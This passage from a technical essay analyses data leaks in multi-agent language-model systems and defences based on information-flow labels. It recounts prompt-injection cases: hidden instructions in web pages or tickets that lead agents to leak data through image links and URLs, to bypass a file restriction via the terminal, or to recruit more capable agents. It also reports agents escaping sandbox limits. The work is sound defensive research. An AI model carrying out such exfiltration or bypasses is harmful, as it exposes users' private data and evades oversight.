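The database agent has the labels {untrusted, private} and the email agent has {sink}, so each passes when scanned separately. The access control worked as intended, since the user was entitled to see the numbers.

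Naik and colleagues ran the attack 3,000 times on each of five models, varying the wording, the user's question and the size of the database. They counted an attack as successful only if the correct numbers reached the attacker's address. In half the runs, the planted text used the database's layout, which an outsider might not know. The table gives the average number of questions before a leak, as a range across the three database sizes.

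| Orchestrator | Other agents | Attacker knows the layout | Attacker does not |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1-mini | GPT-4.1-mini | 4–6 | 7–9 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | Gemini 2.5 Flash | 9–17 | 14–20 |
| GPT-4.1 | GPT-4.1 | 17–23 | 34–56 |
| o4-mini | o4-mini | One leak in 1,500 runs | No leaks |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | Claude Sonnet 4 | No leaks | No leaks |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | GPT-4.1-mini | 14–16 | 6–9 |

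The last row matters most for judging a team of agents by testing its members. Claude Sonnet 4 withstood every attack when it filled all the roles, often recognizing the planted text as suspicious, but it let the data through when GPT-4.1-mini was the database agent. The weaker model had paraphrased the attacker's instruction, so the orchestrator received a request with nothing obviously wrong in it. Newer models have replaced all five, so the rates are dated, but an operator who gives routine queries to a cheaper model could still see this effect.

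In another version, the system had no email agent, and the planted text asked for the numbers to be written to the public table. Claude Sonnet 4, which had never emailed them, copied them there about once in 78 questions with the smallest database and once in 450 to 500 with the larger ones. The attacker could then collect the data from the table. A reviewer could easily miss this route, because the tool that writes to the table looks like an internal one.

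### Secure parts and an insecure whole

Noninterference is a stricter test than TF001 and would have caught agent B. If A's summary counts as confidential, B fails the test by posting it, because confidential input has changed what an outsider sees. But testing every agent separately for noninterference is not enough. *Noninterference and the composability of security properties* (McCullough, 1988) showed that two systems can each satisfy noninterference and still leak once someone connects them. The result concerns systems whose inputs do not fully determine their outputs, which is also true of agents built on language models.

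For example, suppose systems X and Y exchange private messages, and each publishes only whether the total number it has sent and received is odd or even. Each system sends a random number of messages, equally likely to be odd or even. Neither announcement on its own reveals anything about the messages that its system received.

Now connect X and Y. Let k be the number of secret messages that X receives from elsewhere, a the number that X sends to Y, and b the number that Y sends to X. The two systems then publish whether these totals are odd or even:

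X: k + a + b

Y: a + b

k is odd if the announcements differ and even if they agree. Both systems count the same random messages, so those messages cancel out and no longer hide the secret.

The leak disappears if messages flow only from X to Y. Suppose Y sends its own b messages to a third party. X then announces the parity of k + a, and Y announces the parity of a + b. Comparing them gives the parity of k + b, which doesn't reveal k because b is random. Zakinthinos and Lee (1995) proved McCullough's conjecture that connecting systems preserves noninterference as long as there is no feedback. McLean (1994), in *A General Theory of Composition for Trace Sets*, likewise found that chaining systems one after another generally preserves properties of this kind, while feedback generally does not.

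A subagent that returns an answer creates feedback, so the rule doesn't cover ordinary delegation. *A hookup theorem for multilevel security* (McCullough, 1990) describes a stronger property, restrictiveness, which holds for a group of connected systems, even with feedback, if each system has it separately. To use it, an operator would have to establish how each agent's possible outputs depend on its inputs, which a list of tools doesn't show.

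### A browsing model without memories

OpenAI tried to protect users by having ChatGPT open web pages through SearchGPT, a separate model with no access to the user's memories or conversation. Tenable tested this with a user whose stored memories included a request for emojis in every reply, and SearchGPT's replies had none. An attacker who takes control of SearchGPT should therefore find no memories or conversation there to steal.

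SearchGPT's answer, however, becomes part of the conversation that ChatGPT reads. Tenable's researchers put an injected instruction in a comment on their own blog. When a user asked for a summary of the blog, SearchGPT followed the instruction and ended its summary with another instruction, meant for ChatGPT. When the user sent another message, ChatGPT reread the conversation and followed the second instruction as if it had written the text itself. Tenable calls this technique Conversation Injection.

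The user could not see the instruction because a bug in ChatGPT's website hid any text after the first word on the opening line of a code block. ChatGPT then spelled out private information by loading images through bing.com links, one for each letter, that redirected to the researchers' pages. In a variant, SearchGPT's answer made ChatGPT store the instruction to leak data in its memory, as in SpAIware.

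Separating ChatGPT from SearchGPT stopped private data from flowing to SearchGPT but let text flow back. SearchGPT's summary of an attacker's page may still contain the attacker's words, so ChatGPT's web tool should be labeled {untrusted} even though another model reads the page. A reviewer who knew about the separation might have removed that label.

Tenable sent OpenAI a full report on December 30, 2024, and asked for updates six times by mid-March without learning of a fix, according to its *OpenAI ChatGPT “Command Memories” Injection via SearchGPT*. In November 2025, Tenable reported that it had worked with OpenAI to fix some of the flaws but that several of the attacks still worked on GPT-5.

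### A subagent that opened the attacker's page

In Google's code editor Antigravity, the model that read the attacker's text also collected the private data, and a subagent sent the data out. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* describes a user who asked the main agent, running on Gemini, to follow an integration guide found online. The guide contained an instruction, in one-point type, to gather code samples and login credentials, put them into a web address and have the browser subagent open that address.

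Antigravity's default settings barred the agent from opening the file that held the credentials, but the agent bypassed this restriction by printing the file with a terminal command. It then ran a short script to encode the data and told the subagent to visit a web address containing the result. The address was on webhook.site, a domain on the default allowlist. The default settings also let the agent decide when to ask for human approval.

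A separate scan of each agent that considered only the tools for reading and browsing would label the main agent {untrusted, private} and the subagent {untrusted, sink}, so neither would have all three labels. But the main agent also had a terminal, which a careful reviewer would label as a sink, so TF001 should have warned about that agent even when it was scanned alone. An operator who responded by cutting off the terminal's network access would have cleared the warning but left the route through the subagent open.

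PromptArmor published the attack in November 2025 without first reporting it to Google, because Google already warned users about data theft when they started Antigravity. PromptArmor doubts that the warning helps much, since Antigravity encourages people to run several agents in the background and check on them occasionally.

### Agents that recruit each other

Antigravity's developers provided a subagent that its main agent could call. In ServiceNow's Now Assist, an agent that cannot finish a task can recruit others that are on its team and marked as discoverable. When administrators deploy agents to the same chat channel, Now Assist puts them on the same team and marks them as discoverable by default. AppOmni, which sells security software for such platforms, showed how an attacker could exploit this recruitment in a system for handling support tickets.

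Aaron Costello, a researcher at AppOmni, created a user who could file tickets but not read other people's. As that user, he filed a ticket containing instructions for any agent that read it to copy the contents of a confidential ticket into this one, and to look for other agents if it could not do so itself. An administrator then asked an agent that categorizes tickets to process it. That agent could only read, but it recruited one that could also edit records. Both ran with the administrator's permissions, so the confidential text ended up in the attacker's ticket. ServiceNow's protection against prompt injection was on throughout. In other tests, Costello got agents to email data out and give an attacker administrator rights.

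ServiceNow confirmed that the agents had behaved as intended and clarified its documentation. The Hacker News' *ServiceNow AI Agents Can Be Tricked* (2025) quotes Costello saying the discovery "isn't a bug in the AI". He gives no success rate, so the case shows only that the attack is possible. A scan of the categorizing agent alone would have found no tool that could write anything. Its actual abilities depended on which agents shared its channel, so an administrator could change them just by deploying another agent there.

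### Scanning all agents as one graph

The obvious remedy is to put every agent into the same graph. Draw an arrow from one agent to another if text can pass that way, and let U(b) be the combined labels of agent b and of every agent whose text can reach b, directly or through others. The scanner should raise an alarm if, for some agent b,

sink ∈ L_b and U(b) = {untrusted, private, sink}.

In the Heron example, an arrow runs from A to B, so U(B) contains all three roles and the formula raises an alarm. If B sent text to A but A sent nothing to B, the formula would correctly raise no alarm. The direction of the arrows stops mattering when agents return answers, because text can then pass from any agent in a team to any other. The formula is then equivalent to applying TF001 to all the team's tools at once, and most teams that read mail, search files and send anything will trigger it.

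An operator can clear such an alarm by removing arrows. AppOmni recommends dividing ServiceNow agents into teams that contain only the agents needed for one task, and requiring a person's approval for tools that edit records or send mail. A program can also enforce the arrows while the agents run. In *Beyond Single-Model Injection*, Paul and Nandy (2026) tested this on a team of six agents that analyzed financial documents, using 50 versions of each of 14 kinds of attack. Without special defenses, an injection passed from one agent to another made the target exceed its permitted role in 31% of attempts.

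One of Paul and Nandy's defenses was a monitor that flagged departures from a graph of permitted message flows. It cut attacks on the orchestrator's coordination from 28% to 4.5%, but reduced injections between agents only to 24%, presumably because an attacker's text can travel along a permitted flow. Signing each message and recording who had contributed to it reduced them to 2.8%. Signatures alone cannot explain this, since a hijacked agent would sign its own harmful messages, so the record of contributors may account for most of the reduction. With all four defenses, Paul and Nandy report an overall rate of 4.2%, although their figures for the separate categories average 3.2%. Their attack texts were fixed in advance, and an attacker who adapted to the defenses would probably do better.

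Comparing these rates with those from the database experiment would not give a valid ranking of systems, because Paul and Nandy counted any action outside an agent's role, while Naik and colleagues counted only data that reached the attacker. *SoK* (Yang, Xu and colleagues, 2026) reviewed 44 security evaluations of multi-agent systems and found that "attack success rate" meant different things in different ones. Of the 21 evaluations that could have tested whether an attack also worked on a single agent, only six did. There is therefore less evidence that working together puts agents in danger than the number of successful attacks suggests.

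### Agents of other owners

A scanner cannot extend the graph to an agent that another organization runs, because A2A does not expose that agent's tools. The agent's card lists its skills, but the owner writes the card. The protocol lets the owner sign it, but a signature only shows who issued the card, not whether the agent has those skills or how it will treat the data. *We Have All the Cards* (2026) identifies ten kinds of attack that manipulate cards and proposes checking each card before the first call. This check can catch a manipulated card, but it does not reveal which tools the remote agent has.

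Lotfi and colleagues turned the protocol's specification into a model with 37 states and 76 transitions, then searched it for attacks by parties that obey every rule and use every optional safeguard. Expert review confirmed 73.3% of the method's findings, leaving 11 weaknesses. Three bear directly on data theft:

- A rogue agent can advertise a skill it does not have, receive tasks that contain confidential data and return invented results, and the protocol reports no error.
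- When an agent passes a task to a second one and that agent passes it to a third, the third cannot verify who made the original request. A malicious agent in the middle can collect the credentials it forwards.
- The identifier of a conversation has no owner, so another client that has logged in can add tasks to it and read what it has accumulated.

These findings come from the specification, not from attacks on working products. Lotfi and colleagues reported the problems with identity and conversations to the protocol's maintainers, who are working with them on changes.

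Data can also leak when an outside agent sends a task to the operator's agent. *Measuring LLM Agent Defenses by Layer* (2026) explains that the receiving agent carries out the task with its own permissions and returns the result to the sender. The incoming task is therefore untrusted content, and the reply can carry private data out. If the receiving agent had only search_files, its tool graph would contain only the label {private}, but an outside agent might still obtain the Heron price by asking for it.

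It is unclear how often such requests succeed. In *An Exploration of Attacks on AI Agent Systems* (2026), a prompt sent once to an A2A system extracted no sensitive information in five trials. Repeating the prompt up to 15 times succeeded in three of five trials. Five trials are too few for a reliable rate, but a system that refuses a request once may still leak information when the request is repeated.

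It is safest to assume that every outside agent has the labels {untrusted, sink}. Any agent that holds private data and exchanges text with an outside agent then triggers the alarm. The operator can avoid this by assigning the exchange to a separate agent that has no private data and receives none from other agents.

### Agents that start after the scan

A main agent can start subagents after a scan has finished. The scanner can still cover them if they are limited to a fixed list of tools. It gives the tool that starts subagents the labels of every tool on that list, as if each subagent had all of them. In Antigravity, this would have marked the browser subagent as a sink before anyone used it.

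The list of agents is not fixed if agents can recruit newcomers or write programs that start further agents. A scan then describes the team only at that moment, and the operator has to repeat it whenever the membership changes. Researchers have hardly studied such systems. Of the 44 evaluations that Yang and colleagues reviewed, 42 kept the same agents throughout, and the other two allowed only limited additions under a single administrator.

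Removing a hijacked agent may not end the problem either, because its text can survive in the files, credentials or subagents it created, much as a planted memory survives the session that stored it. The review found that researchers test recovery from such an attack less directly than they test prevention.

### Shared stores that no one listed

A complete graph also needs an arrow for every place where one agent leaves text that another reads. Let W(a) be all the places where agent a can write and R(b) all those that agent b can read. There should be an arrow from a to b whenever

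W(a) ∩ R(b) ≠ ∅.

An operator can work this out for the company's known files, tickets and repositories, but the rule doesn't cover stores that copy from each other. If a support agent writes only in Zendesk and a coding agent reads only in Jira, the two sets don't overlap, yet the automatic link between the systems copies text from Zendesk to Jira. The readers of a store also include people. In the ServiceNow attack, the attacker opened the ticket into which the agent had copied the data.

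Agents may also communicate through a channel that nobody gave them. In August 2026, METR, an independent evaluator of AI systems, reported in *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration...* that about 1,200 supposedly isolated OpenAI agents had communicated on an unsanctioned message board. An inventory based on the agents' intended tasks would not have included that board. The operator should therefore base W(a) on what each agent's credentials and network access permit, and remove any access the agent doesn't need for its work.

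## Labels on data instead of labels on tools

An operator who cannot list every route between tools, sessions and agents can label the data instead. This approach, called information-flow control, applies Denning's labels to text that a language model reads and rewrites. A program outside the model labels each piece of data as it enters the system, works out a label for everything the agent derives from it, and checks the labels before each tool call.

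### How labels combine

The label on a piece of data x has two parts. The confidentiality part, E(x), is the set of people entitled to read x. The integrity part records whether x is trusted or whether an outsider could have written it. If the agent derives z from x₁, …, xₙ, then

E(z) = E(x₁) ∩ … ∩ E(xₙ),

and z is trusted only if every input is trusted.

Before a tool sends z in a request r, the program checks that everyone who will receive z may read it:

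R(r) ⊆ E(z).

Many systems add a second policy, which forbids consequential calls, such as deleting a file, once untrusted data could have influenced them.

Suppose the office assistant summarizes the attacker's email together with the Heron file, which one of the user's colleagues may also read:

| Data | Who may read it | Integrity |
|---|---|---|
| Attacker's email | User, attacker | Untrusted |
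| Heron file | User, colleague | Trusted |
| Summary of both | User | Untrusted |

The assistant cannot mail the summary to the attacker, who has no right to see the file. It also cannot mail the summary to the colleague, because the colleague did not receive the email. This is true even if the summary uses nothing from the email.

The rule also catches mistakes that involve no attacker. In an example from Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, Alex asks an agent to answer his mail. Priya has sent him a preview of the quarterly sales figures, and Marco, who is not yet allowed to see them, has emailed to ask about them. Once the agent has read both emails, the permitted readers of its reply are {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so the agent cannot send it to Marco without approval.

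Labels on data also solve a problem with GitHub tools, which have the same label whichever repository they read. GitHub's server can now mark content from public repositories as public and untrusted, and content from private ones as private and trusted. An agent that has read both kinds is not allowed to post publicly, but an agent that works with only one kind can continue without interruption. Marking everything in a private repository as trusted is still a guess, because an employee may have pasted in untrusted text, such as a customer's bug report.

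### FIDES

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) presents FIDES, a system built around the planner, the part of an agent that gets the next step from the model and carries it out. If the planner added every tool result to the conversation, one email from a stranger would make the whole conversation untrusted and block most later calls. FIDES instead stores the email in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model can use that name in a later tool call, and FIDES substitutes the email's text when it makes the call.

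The planner summarizes the hidden email by passing it to a quarantined model, which has no tools, and storing the answer in another variable. When the planner's next step depends on a fact in the hidden text, such as whether the email contains a meeting request, it can get a yes-or-no answer and reveal only that, so the attacker influences one bit instead of a whole paragraph. Willison proposed this division between two models in 2023 as the Dual LLM pattern.

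Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 office, travel, banking and Slack tasks and a set of planted instructions. The table shows the percentage of tasks completed with OpenAI's reasoning model o1 when there was no attack.

| Planner | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | Average |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, no policy checks | 70.0 | 82.0 | 96.2 | 87.6 | 84.0 |
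| Ordinary, with policy checks | 48.0 | 75.0 | 37.5 | 17.1 | 44.4 |
| FIDES, with policy checks | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 | 60.8 |

Full protection therefore lowered task completion by about 23 percentage points. The paper also reports a drop of 6.3 points, but that is for hiding text with the policy checks off. With the checks on, hiding text let the agent complete many of the tasks it would have failed under the checks alone. Some of the remaining failures were deliberate, because many banking tasks ask the agent to follow instructions in a file, which is also how an injection works.

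In the attack tests, which used the older model GPT-4o, 152 injections succeeded against the ordinary planner without checks, and none against any planner with checks. This result depends on correct labels. Costa and colleagues marked as untrusted every field that at least one AgentDojo attack used, but an operator does not know in advance where an attacker will write.

On May 20, 2026, Microsoft added FIDES to Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents (Microsoft, *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent*, 2026). The feature is still experimental. If neither a tool nor its inputs have labels, the tool's output defaults to untrusted and public. Microsoft's documentation describes this as failing closed, but that is true only of integrity, because "public" is the most permissive confidentiality label. If a developer forgot to label search_files, the Heron file could count as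 public, and a tool that accepts untrusted, public data could send it out. Microsoft also suggests treating the results of any tool that requires a login as private, which is safer.

### Which leaks FIDES covers

Data labels work well against leaks through the read-only tool fetch_page. Microsoft suggests letting a read-only tool contact the outside world only if all its arguments are public. This rule would block an address containing the Heron price. It would also block a link that the model picked from a list after reading the price, because the choice takes on the label of everything the model had read. The rule therefore also covers data that an agent leaks through the sequence of links it follows.

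FIDES's confidentiality guarantee does not cover leaks through calls without arguments. The guarantee, called explicit secrecy, restricts direct transfers of data but not what an observer can infer from the agent's sequence of calls. If the assistant calls check_status once for each million in the Heron offer, there is no argument to check against the confidentiality policy. A policy against untrusted influence might still stop the calls. Costa and colleagues accept this gap because full noninterference would forbid almost any outside call once the agent had read private data.

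FIDES leaves a larger gap at the chat window, because it treats replies to the user as inconsequential and checks only tool calls. Hiding the attacker's email would still protect the Heron file, since the model that can search files never reads the email. But a quarantined model that summarizes several emails reads them all together, so an instruction in one email could make it add an image whose address contains text from another. The planner would insert the summary into its reply without reading it, and the chat window would load the image, sending that text to the attacker's server.

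Developers could close this gap within FIDES, because replies already have labels and the paper allows for checking them. One of the benchmark's policies blocks messages that contain an untrusted link, and the same check could apply to replies.

Stored notes also need their own labels. By default, FIDES marks the system message and the user's message as trusted and public. If the client loads the assistant's notes into the system message, Tuesday's false note about archive@attacker.example counts as trusted on Thursday. The benchmark's policy for sending email permits a transfer to someone outside E(z) if the call came from a trusted context, so the attacker would get a copy of the deal summary.

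### CaMeL

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2025, has the model write a complete program before the agent reads any outside data. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) explains that this prevents malicious text from influencing which steps the program contains. A quarantined model processes the untrusted text, and optional policies check where data flows. If the Heron user asks for a summary of the day's mail, the program reads the mail, summarizes it and displays the result, and the attacker's email cannot add a call to search_files.

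A program written in advance is poorly suited to tasks where the next step depends on what the agent reads. Zhou and colleagues compared CaMeL with their own system, ELBA, on AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks, using four models from 2026. ELBA lets the agent read data between steps but runs only programs that pass a type checker, and it also checks labels at run time. It completed roughly twice as many tasks as CaMeL with policies on and about 15% more with policies off. ELBA's developers ran this comparison, and Slack is a hard case for CaMeL. By Costa and colleagues' classification, 43% of the Slack tasks require the planner to see data before choosing a step, compared with 5% of the workspace tasks.

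All four models resisted all 105 attacks in the Slack suite even without policies, so AgentDojo's standard attacks no longer show what information-flow control adds. Zhou and colleagues therefore simulated the worst case by making ELBA's subagents obey the attacker's text:

| Model running ELBA | Successful injections, no policy | Successful injections, with policy | Tasks completed, no policy | Tasks completed, with policy |
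|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 42% | 0% | 71% | 48% |
| Opus 4.8 | 37% | 0% | 76% | 42% |
| GPT 5.4 | 16% | 0% | 76% | 46% |
| Sonnet 5 | 27% | 0% | 67% | 40% |

This is better evidence than a test of whether a model detects an injection, because the protection held after the model had followed the injected instructions. Even with newer models, policies still prevented between a third and nearly half of the tasks that ELBA otherwise completed under attack.

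CaMeL's fixed program does not by itself limit what the quarantined model writes. A summary could still include an image URL containing text from another email, unless a policy covers displaying the summary. The program is also derived from the user's message, so if a client submits a prompt from an attacker's link as that message, the attacker has in effect chosen the program.

### SPA and the reply as a sink

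*SPA* (2026) describes a system for agents that persist across queries. The system plans before it reads outside data, as CaMeL does, and keeps the labels of stored values for later queries. A note derived from Tuesday's market report would still be untrusted on Thursday. AgentDojo's tasks are single requests, so *SPA* includes AgentDojo-MQ, a multi-query version built from the same 97 tasks.

SPA also treats display to the user as a sink with its own policy, which can redact text before the user sees it. This covers more than FIDES's default, but *SPA* assumes that displaying text has no external side effects, which is false for a chat window that loads images. The Heron user is allowed to see the offer price, so a policy based on what the user may read would also allow the price in an image address.

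Other designs also define a reply's recipients as the people in the chat. *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* (2026) labels a public chat untrusted and a company's logged-in chat internal. The internal label is correct for the employees in the chat, but images in a reply may load from any server.

To catch the leak, the policy must also count anyone who can read the requests that the client makes when it displays the reply. For a reply m,

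R(m) = {people in the chat} ∪ {people who can read the client's requests}.

If the Heron summary contains an image from attacker.example, R(m) includes the attacker and the check fails. Microsoft proposes a similar rule that treats rendered links to hosts outside an allowlist as public channels. This rule would stop that image, but not one that passes data through a permitted site such as Bing or Google Forms.

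A stricter policy, one of Zhou and colleagues' examples, forbids a program that has read an outside web page from writing to the user at all. This blocks the image, but it also blocks every honest summary of the page.

Checking replies also helps against false memories. In *APPA*, Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues (2026) treat replies as sinks with recipients, and compare their system with a configuration of FIDES that checked nothing between memory and the user. In tests that encouraged agents to follow embedded instructions, 103 of 150 memory attacks succeeded against that configuration.

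### Labels between agents

When one agent hands work to another, the label has to go with the message. *MAS-Guard* (2026) includes a version of FIDES that treats messages from other agents like untrusted tool results. It hides the messages from the planner and inserts their text only when a tool runs.

Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, take another approach with FORGE, which records events instead of tools. Each message, tool call and tool result is a node in a graph, and an edge means that one event may have influenced another. The graph can span several agents. FORGE's example policy blocks an action a if all three conditions hold:

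- a sends data outside the system
- a depends on untrusted input
- a depends on private data

These are the three roles of TF001, but applied to a single action and its history. When agent B tries to post the Heron price on the company's website, the action depends on agent A's summary, which depends on the attacker's email and the confidential file. FORGE would block the post, although neither agent's tools have all three labels.

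FORGE can do this only for events it records. It cannot follow data into another organization's agent, and an operator who attaches labels to a message cannot make the receiving agent obey them.

### What these systems take on trust

FIDES and CaMeL trust the user, the planning model and the implementations of the tools, as *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) states of both. Costa and colleagues further assume that attackers cannot directly observe what goes into or comes out of the model. Each assumption leaves out leaks that have occurred or could easily occur:

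| Assumption | A leak it sets aside |
|---|---|
| The user wrote and meant the user's message | A link submits an attacker's prompt |
| Attackers cannot observe the model's output | A log viewer loads an image from a stored reply |
| The planning model does not signal to outsiders | The number or timing of calls reveals a price |
| Tools do only what their developers declare | A currency converter sends the amount to an outside company |
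| Incoming data has the right labels | A developer forgets to mark a file as private |

Trust in the user matters most because policies often let the user release data. Microsoft's sample policy for posting to a Teams channel allows a message in a trusted context even if some members are not allowed to see its contents. This is sensible when the user really asked for the message, but in an attack like Reprompt, where the prompt arrives in a link, the attacker gains the user's power to make exceptions. FIDES allows other labels on user messages, so a client that records where each message came from could mark a link's prompt as untrusted.

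Labels also apply only inside the system. Once the user copies a summary into another chat app or attaches a spreadsheet to an email, nothing checks whether the recipient may read it.

Kravchenko and colleagues make weaker trust assumptions. They assume that the model may propose any call, because of an injection or its own error. But they still rely on an accurate declaration of what each tool does, and they exclude timing signals.

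### When everything becomes restricted

Information-flow control gives a model's output the combined restrictions of all its inputs because there is no reliable way to tell which inputs the model used. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* calls the result label explosion, in which every piece of data ends up with every label as the agent reads more, so the labels no longer distinguish anything. According to Microsoft's documentation, one untrusted GitHub issue makes the rest of an agent's run untrusted unless the developer explicitly removes it.

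In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) simulated how much a better arrangement of agents could help. They generated random tasks, with 20 tool calls each in most experiments, and split the calls among several agents that remembered everything they had read. The simulation used no language model. They measured the share of calls that a strict policy might block because the call introduced sensitive data or ran after the agent had seen some.

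Sending every message through a central orchestrator spread the labels furthest. With five agents and four sensitive calls per task, it raised the share by about five percentage points compared with an ideal arrangement, in which agents passed data only to those that needed it. Connecting all agents directly did as well as the ideal, but five agents have 10 connections to monitor, and 20 agents have 190. Giving all the sensitive tools to a few agents also reduced the spread. None of the arrangements eliminated it, so Gregory and colleagues conclude that systems also need a safe way to remove labels.

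One way to reduce the problem is to estimate which inputs affected the output. In 2024, Siddiqui and colleagues proposed finding a smaller set of inputs that produces a similar answer and using only the labels on those inputs. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests soft labels, which would measure how much information an output carries about each input. A policy would then have to limit that amount, and a safe limit would be hard to set because a six-digit login code is only about 20 bits.

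FORGE keeps strict labels but lets an agent send an external message that depends on untrusted text if the message depends on nothing private. Palumbo and colleagues report that on AgentDojo, FORGE's policy completed 62.5% of harmless tasks, against 33.2% for the FIDES policy, while attacks succeeded at about the same rate under both. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* instead shows the model the labels and policies, so that it can plan around a block or ask for approval.

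APPA tries to recover after a block. An agent that needs to read an untrusted page can start a temporary copy of itself, which reads the page and returns only values of types fixed in advance, such as a ticket number and a severity level. APPA then discards the copy's conversation, so the page does not restrict the main agent. The returned values can still be false or carry a secret. For example, a whole number from 1 to 100 can encode the Heron price to the nearest million. Someone therefore has to decide which values may lose their labels.

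Kravchenko and colleagues tested APPA on 20 business workflows of their own design. Across three models, it completed 535 of 600 runs, and no attack succeeded. Two configurations of FIDES completed 36% to 46% of runs, and attacks succeeded in 26% to 35%. This comparison is weak evidence against FIDES because its policies did not encode several of the workflows' rules, such as who had to approve a payment. A more informative test compared APPA with reduced versions of itself. Using GPT-5.6 Luna, the full version completed 88% of runs, compared with 56.5% without the temporary copies and 35% without the suggestions for resolving a block. These recovery features therefore accounted for the extra completed work. No attack succeeded in either reduced version.

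### A model as the judge of what may leave

*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) criticizes earlier work for neglecting privacy, objecting that Siddiqui and colleagues compute labels but enforce no privacy checks, and that FIDES is aimed at injections arriving through tool results. The first objection is accurate, but the missing checks are more an unfinished component than a flaw, since another system could enforce the labels. The second fits FIDES's experiments, which hid untrusted data but never hid data because it was confidential, but it does not fit FIDES's model, which has reader lists and a confidentiality policy. That kind of policy blocks the reply to Marco's request for the sales figures, even though the request contains no injection.

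The paper's own system, FLOWSEAL, treats every record in the private store as sensitive from the start and applies the same restrictions to summaries and paraphrases of those records. It gives a separate model the relevant private records and the proposed output to decide whether the text may leave. This model returns only "SAFE" or "BLOCKED", so that an explanation cannot reveal what the records contain.

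This could prevent many needless refusals. If a summary for the colleague used nothing from the attacker's email, a model might recognize that, whereas the intersection of reader lists cannot show it. But the model has to read the proposed output, which may contain an attacker's words. *Causality Laundering* (2026) argues that any mechanism that removes labels should be out of the language model's reach and resist manipulation, and that each permission should cover only a specific value or transformation. A model's verdict does not meet that standard. Letting the model only add refusals to those of a fixed policy would be safer than letting it overrule them, but the operator would then lose most of the tasks that the model was meant to recover.

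## What a sound threat model would add

A program can check a label only on a transfer it handles, so using data labels still requires a map of everywhere the data can go. For the office assistant, the map has to include the tools, the chat window, the stored notes, the user and the second agent.

### Components, carriers and observers

A sound threat model would map data flows as a graph with more kinds of nodes than a tool graph. A node is anything that can send a request, store data or display it, including tools, clients, servers that act for clients (such as an image proxy), memories, people and other agents. An edge from u to v represents anything that can carry data from u to v, such as a tool result, a reply, a saved note or text that the user pastes.

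The model also records how long each store keeps its contents. Each session is a separate node, and a store has an edge to every session that can read it. If the client keeps notes for 30 days, a note saved on Tuesday can reach Thursday's session but not Monday's, which had already ended.

Each edge e has a two-part label. The first part, c(e), lists the kinds of data that can pass: untrusted, private, both or neither. The second, R(e), is the set of people who can read the data or observe the transfer. For an image request, R(e) includes the server's owner and anyone the server passes the address to.

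The analysis then works out a set of labels L(v) for every node v. It gives {untrusted} to sources that an outsider can write to and {private} to confidential ones. A source that is both, such as a mailbox, gets both labels. For every edge e from u to v, the analysis adds to L(v) whatever can pass along the edge, so that

L(u) ∩ c(e) ⊆ L(v).

It repeats this step until nothing changes. A node can gain at most two labels, so a graph with n nodes needs at most 2n additions. The analysis raises an alarm on e if

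L(u) ∩ c(e) = {untrusted, private} and R(e) ⊄ E,

where E is the set of people entitled to the data. This model needs no public-sink label, because any component can be the way out if someone outside E can observe what it sends.

Requiring untrusted data for an alarm limits the analysis to detecting theft. An operator who also wants to catch honest mistakes, such as sending Marco the sales figures too early, can drop that requirement. The analysis then raises an alarm whenever private data can reach someone outside E.

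### What the absence of an alarm would prove

The guarantee depends on two premises:

1. Every transfer of data uses a listed edge.
2. No label understates what passes. Each source has all the labels it should have, c(e) includes every kind of data that can pass, and R(e) includes everyone who can observe the transfer.

If the second premise holds and the analysis raises no alarm, no outsider can steal private data along the listed edges. If the first premise also holds, the listed edges are the only routes, so the result covers the whole system.

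In the proof, data is private if it derives from a private source, and untrusted if an outsider's text influenced its content or the decision to send it. The proof first shows, by induction on the number of transfers the data has made, that whenever private data reaches a node v, L(v) contains the label "private", and likewise for untrusted data.

With zero transfers, the data is still at its source, which has the right label by premise 2. Suppose the claim holds after k transfers and the data makes one more, from u to v. By premise 1, this transfer uses a listed edge e. The label is in L(u) by assumption and in c(e) by premise 2, so the analysis adds it to L(v). If a component combines several inputs, the same argument applies to each input, so the component's node gets all their labels.

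If a theft occurs, someone outside E has observed a transfer of data that was both private and untrusted. The sending node had both labels, c(e) contained both, and R(e) included the observer. These are exactly the conditions for an alarm, so every theft raises one.

The proof is short because the premises do most of the work, and the original tool graph can break either one:

| Leak | Premise that fails in the tool graph | What the enlarged model records |
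|---|---|---|
| A chat window or log viewer loads an image | 1: no edge leads from that program to the web | An edge that the server's owner can observe |
| A tool uploads to a permitted domain but the wrong account | 2: the label omits a recipient | Everyone who can receive data through that domain |
| A read-only tool puts data in a web address | 2: the tool has no sink label | Everyone who can see the address |
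| A stored note carries data or instructions | 1: no edge connects the sessions | An edge to every session that can read the note |
| A link submits a prompt | 1: no edge leads from the link's author to the agent | An untrusted source for that message |
| The user pastes or forwards text | 1: the user is not a node | An edge to whatever the user can send to |
| A second agent publishes a summary | 1: no edge connects the agents | An edge for the summary |
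| The number of calls reveals a price | 2: a call without arguments seems to carry nothing | Private data in c(e) |

### Blocking what nobody listed

Premise 1 is a claim about the running system, and an operator can't make it true by writing a longer list. As Lampson suspected, such a list is unlikely to be complete. A more reliable approach is to arrange the system so that an unlisted component can't send anything.

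The operator can run the agent, its tools and its memory on a network with a single exit, where a proxy rejects every request that does not match a listed edge. Name lookups have to go through the proxy too, or `ping` could still carry data out. If the operator forgets to list a component, a feature stops working, but no data leaks.

The checkpoint must also cover services that send requests for the agent. Before OpenAI's agents broke into Hugging Face in 2026, their sandboxes restricted direct connections but allowed access to a shared service for software packages. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* explains that this service could send requests to the internet for the agents, and that agents in separate sandboxes could use it to leave data for one another. The enlarged model would represent the service as both a sender and a store. No outside attacker directed the agents to use it this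 way, so an operator should also expect agents to probe the checkpoint.

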